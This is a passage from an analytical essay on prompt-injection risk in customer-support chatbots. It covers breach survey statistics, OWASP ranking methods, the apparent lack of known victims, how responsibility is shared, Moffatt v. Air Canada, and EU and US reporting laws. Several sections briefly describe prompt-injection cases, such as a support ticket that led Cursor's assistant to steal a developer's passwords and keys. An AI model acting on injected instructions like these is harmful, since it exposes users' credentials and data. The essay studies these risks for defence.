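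A second NIST project, a guide to applying its Cybersecurity Framework to AI, is further along. The preliminary draft includes customer service among its examples, according to Inside Privacy's *NIST Publishes Preliminary Draft of Cybersecurity Framework Profile for Artificial Intelligence*. Comments closed in January 2026, and NIST planned to release a fuller public draft that year. In November, NIST's *Cyber SI Profile* still listed the project's status as "Reviewing Comments".

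Deployers therefore don't yet have an official US checklist for support chatbots, but that is only a partial excuse for weak security. Security engineers have known for decades that a program should have only the access it needs, and SP 800-53 already requires this. Tallow Lane can tie its order lookup to the login without waiting for a new standard.

### What the breach surveys measure

IBM's yearly survey suggests that many companies have not taken such steps. For the 2026 edition, the Ponemon Institute studied 602 breached organizations in 16 countries, according to SecureWorld's *2026 Cost of a Data Breach Report* (2026). IBM's *AI‑powered adversaries and the enterprise risk challenge* (2026) reports that about one in five had experienced an attack on an AI model or application, and that 92% of those lacked proper access controls for AI.

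The year before, 13% of organizations had reported an AI-related breach, according to ASIS International's *Global Data Breach Costs Drop*. IBM's *2025 Cost of a Data Breach Report* (2025) found that 97% of those organizations lacked the controls. Attacks on AI therefore became more common among breached companies, while the controls remained rare among those attacked.

The 92% is hard to interpret without knowing how many other companies lack the same controls. IBM also found that only 40% of organizations used access controls on AI models and data. If the two figures refer to the same controls, about 31% of the organizations without them had an AI-related breach, compared with about 4% of those with them. The controls may not explain the whole gap, because companies that control access to AI are probably careful in other ways too, and a company that has just lost data is more likely to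 judge that its controls were not "proper".

The survey includes only companies that had a breach, so it can't show how likely one is. It also doesn't separate customer-facing chatbots from internal models. But IBM lists causes familiar from the Drift and McHire cases: compromised APIs, vulnerable applications and badly configured cloud services. It found similar rates of incidents whether companies used open-source models or rented them from a vendor. *IBM finds 92% of companies hit by AI security breaches lacked basic access controls* (Joos, 2026) gives the average cost of an incident involving AI as $5.33 million, compared with $4.70 million for other breaches.

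Security is therefore immature partly because organizations don't use tools that already exist. Only the tools for preventing prompt injection or detecting it afterwards are themselves immature.

Most of these figures come from companies that sell a remedy and gain when readers conclude that they need to spend more, though that doesn't make the figures false. IBM's *Cost of a Data Breach Report 2026* (2026) advises companies to control the identities of AI agents and monitor sensitive data, and IBM sells products for protecting and monitoring data. HackerOne puts its figures on AI flaws beside a link to its AI testing service. OWASP is a non-profit, but security vendors sponsor its AI project. Its September announcement quotes Michael Bargury of Zenity, which sells software for monitoring agents, welcoming the rise of "excessive agency" from sixth place to third. Excessive agency means giving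 an AI system more tools, permissions or freedom than its job needs. Gartner sells advice to the kind of managers it surveys.

### Where are the victims?

Even if the tooling is immature, this may not have hurt many people. EchoLeak, SearchLeak, ForcedLeak, BodySnatcher and the attacks on Lenovo's and Eurostar's chatbots were all demonstrations by researchers, with no known victims. In August 2026, even Gerry, whose company profits from concern about such attacks, used the future tense: "You're going to start to see agents getting hacked, not people."

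OWASP's own data gives the skeptic some support, since prompt injection would not have made the 2026 top ten on recorded incidents alone. Members' votes counted for three-quarters of the ranking and incidents for one-quarter. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a security vendor's account of the method, reports that the project collected 7,714 incidents, of which 6,639 had enough detail to classify.

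The weighting explains how it still came first. Suppose each risk gets one score out of ten from the vote and another from incident records. A risk that scores 10 in the vote and 0 in the records gets 7.5 overall, while a risk that scores 6 in the vote and 10 in the records gets only 7.

OWASP argues that the count is low because security teams fight prompt injection hard and "fewer clean exploits reach a public database" as a result. That may be true, but the count would also be low if criminals preferred easier methods or victims never noticed the attacks.

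The records also came from public vulnerability databases, which mostly list flaws in products. These databases can include a flaw that a researcher found and the vendor fixed before anyone exploited it, so an "incident" here may have caused no loss. They probably won't include an attack on one shop's badly built chatbot.

Other databases blur the same distinction. The OECD's entry on ShareLeak and PipeLeak, which is labelled as AI-generated, classifies them as an incident because the flaws were "exploited in practice (not just theoretical)", but Capsule's researchers were the ones who exploited them. Some collections also mix attacks on AI with attacks that use it. SC Media's *AI-driven attacks target governments, cloud agents, supply chains* describes an OWASP round-up that includes a breach of Mexican government agencies. The attackers used Claude and ChatGPT as tools, so the breach is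 not evidence of whether support chatbots are safe.

Some vendors can observe attacks directly. Check Point Research's *AI Security Report 2026* (2026) found that longer malicious prompts, typical of indirect injection, increased about fivefold between March and May 2026, to nearly 1% of the prompts it observed. A detector that wrongly flagged 1% of harmless prompts would produce the same total even if there were no attacks. The increase is harder to explain by false positives, but it could include researchers' tests, and the figure counts detected attempts rather than successful thefts.

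In contrast to the demonstrations, the confirmed thefts through Meta's recovery tool, Salesloft Drift and Fireworks AI did serious harm. In these cases, companies gave chatbots and their suppliers too much power with too few checks. The thefts aren't evidence that prompt injection has caused comparable harm, because the Drift and Fireworks attackers didn't need it, and there is little sign that the Instagram attackers did.

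Some thefts must also go unnoticed. Meta took 44 days to discover its breach, even though the attackers were locking people out of their accounts. An email copied through Copilot would be harder to notice, because the victim keeps both the email and access to the account.

The number of thefts that could have stayed hidden depends on how often such thefts become public. If each has a 5% chance of becoming public, the chance that nobody has heard of any is about 5% after 58 thefts (0.95⁵⁸) and practically zero after 1,000. The 5% disclosure rate is a guess, and spies would be caught less often than criminals, who have to contact their victims to demand a ransom. But the calculation suggests that the lack of known victims is compatible with dozens of hidden thefts and much harder to reconcile with thousands.

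Prompt injection has probably not yet caused widespread harm through business chatbots. That is a weak reason to postpone defenses, because SQL injection attacks also took years to peak.

### Who has to answer for a failure?

Up to four parties can contribute to a failure, and each controls something the others can't change.

| Party | What it controls | A failure it could prevent |
|---|---|---|
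| Model maker | How firmly the model ranks the system prompt above other text | The model reveals a secret when asked to translate its instructions |
| Platform | The chat software, its default settings and its patches | The server accepts a forged conversation history |
| Deployer | The data, tools and permissions the chatbot gets | The order lookup accepts any order number |
| User | Their own login, and which links they open | A stolen password is enough to enter the account |

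Meta filled the first three roles for its support assistant, so it could not shift blame to another company. Most disputes over responsibility are between a platform and a deployer. Salesforce blamed customers' settings for PipeLeak, and ServiceNow said its agents were working as intended. After Zenity used a support ticket to make Cursor's coding assistant steal a developer's passwords and keys, Cursor similarly called this a known issue and said it advised users to review each connection to outside software before installing it.

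Only the deployer knows which of its data is sensitive, but the platform chooses the default settings. A fair division of responsibility would hold the platform responsible for its defaults and the deployer for any changes it makes to them. Under that division, Salesforce and ServiceNow would have been responsible for more than they accepted.

Responsibility is often unclear within the company deploying the chatbot too. HackerOne asked 111 security leaders at large companies what happens when AI gets a security decision wrong. In 39% of the companies, the chief security officer takes the blame, but only 10% have a formal rule for who is responsible for the decision.

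A customer usually deals only with the deployer, and an early ruling held one deployer, Air Canada, responsible for what its chatbot had told a customer. In November 2022, after a grandmother's death, Jake Moffatt asked the chatbot on the airline's website about reduced fares for bereaved travelers. It replied that passengers could buy a ticket at the normal price and apply for the reduction within 90 days, but it linked to a page stating that they couldn't apply after traveling. Moffatt applied after flying, and Air Canada refused the request.

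In *Moffatt v. Air Canada* (2024), British Columbia's Civil Resolution Tribunal, which hears small claims, found the airline liable for negligent misrepresentation by its chatbot. The tribunal understood Air Canada to be arguing that the chatbot was a separate legal entity responsible for its own actions. It rejected this argument because the chatbot was part of the airline's website, and it saw no reason why customers should have to check one part of the website against another. It ordered Air Canada to pay C$812.02, including interest and fees.

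The tribunal's decisions don't bind other courts. Given the date, the chatbot probably didn't use a modern language model, and nobody had attacked it. But the tribunal's reasoning would apply to some attacks. If a planted review led Tallow Lane's chatbot to promise Ines 90 days for returns, she would have relied on the shop's website just as Moffatt relied on the airline's. The shop would have trouble arguing that it took reasonable care if it had let the chatbot present customers' comments as shop policy. The visitor who got a Chevrolet dealer's chatbot to agree to sell a car for $1 has a much weaker case, because someone who dictates an answer can't reasonably claim to have relied on it.

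Deployers may be underestimating misinformation, OWASP's term for false or unsupported answers that people or programs act on. It ranked near the top in the incident records but near the bottom in the members' vote, which Invicti describes as the widest gap in the list.

### Legal duties to report and repair

When personal data leaks, the law in most places requires the deployer to report it. Under the European Union's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), a company must notify the regulator within 72 hours of becoming aware of a breach, unless the breach is unlikely to put people at risk. If the risk is high, it must also tell the people affected. A supplier that handles data for the company must tell the company about a breach without undue delay. In November 2025, the European Commission proposed extending the 72-hour deadline to 96 hours and requiring companies to notify the regulator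 only of high-risk breaches.

The United States has no general federal law of this kind, but every state has its own, which is why Meta wrote to officials in Maine and Nebraska. Most of these laws cover only listed types of data, such as Social Security numbers or account passwords. They might not cover a leaked chat in which Ines mentions that her house will be empty for two weeks, although the chat would normally count as personal data under the GDPR.

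Time limits for reporting a breach generally start when the company discovers it. Meta wrote to Nebraska promptly, five days after discovering its breach, but weeks had passed before the discovery. A company with poor logs can meet its deadline and still leave customers exposed for months. The GDPR separately requires appropriate security, so a regulator can penalize a company for failing to protect data even if it reported the breach on time.

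Laws on the security of the software itself are newer. The EU's Cyber Resilience Act requires manufacturers to report any actively exploited flaw in their products from September 11, 2026. They must send a warning within 24 hours, a fuller notice within 72 hours, and a final report within 14 days of a fix becoming available. Broader duties, such as shipping products with secure default settings, apply from December 2027.

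The duty to report flaws applies only when someone is exploiting them maliciously, so it would not have covered demonstrations such as EchoLeak. The act also covers products more clearly than services. A chatbot plugin that a shop buys and installs on its own server is probably covered, while a chatbot that runs entirely on the supplier's servers generally is not. Tallow Lane rents the second kind, so for now it depends mainly on its contract to make the supplier report and fix flaws.

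The EU has also extended its rules on defective products to software, including AI systems, and given member states until December 9, 2026, to put the change into national law. People will be able to claim compensation for injury, damaged property, and private data that a defective product destroys or corrupts, without having to prove negligence. They can't claim under these rules for a data leak alone. A customer could therefore be compensated under the rules if an attack made an assistant delete their family photographs, but not if the attacker only copied them.
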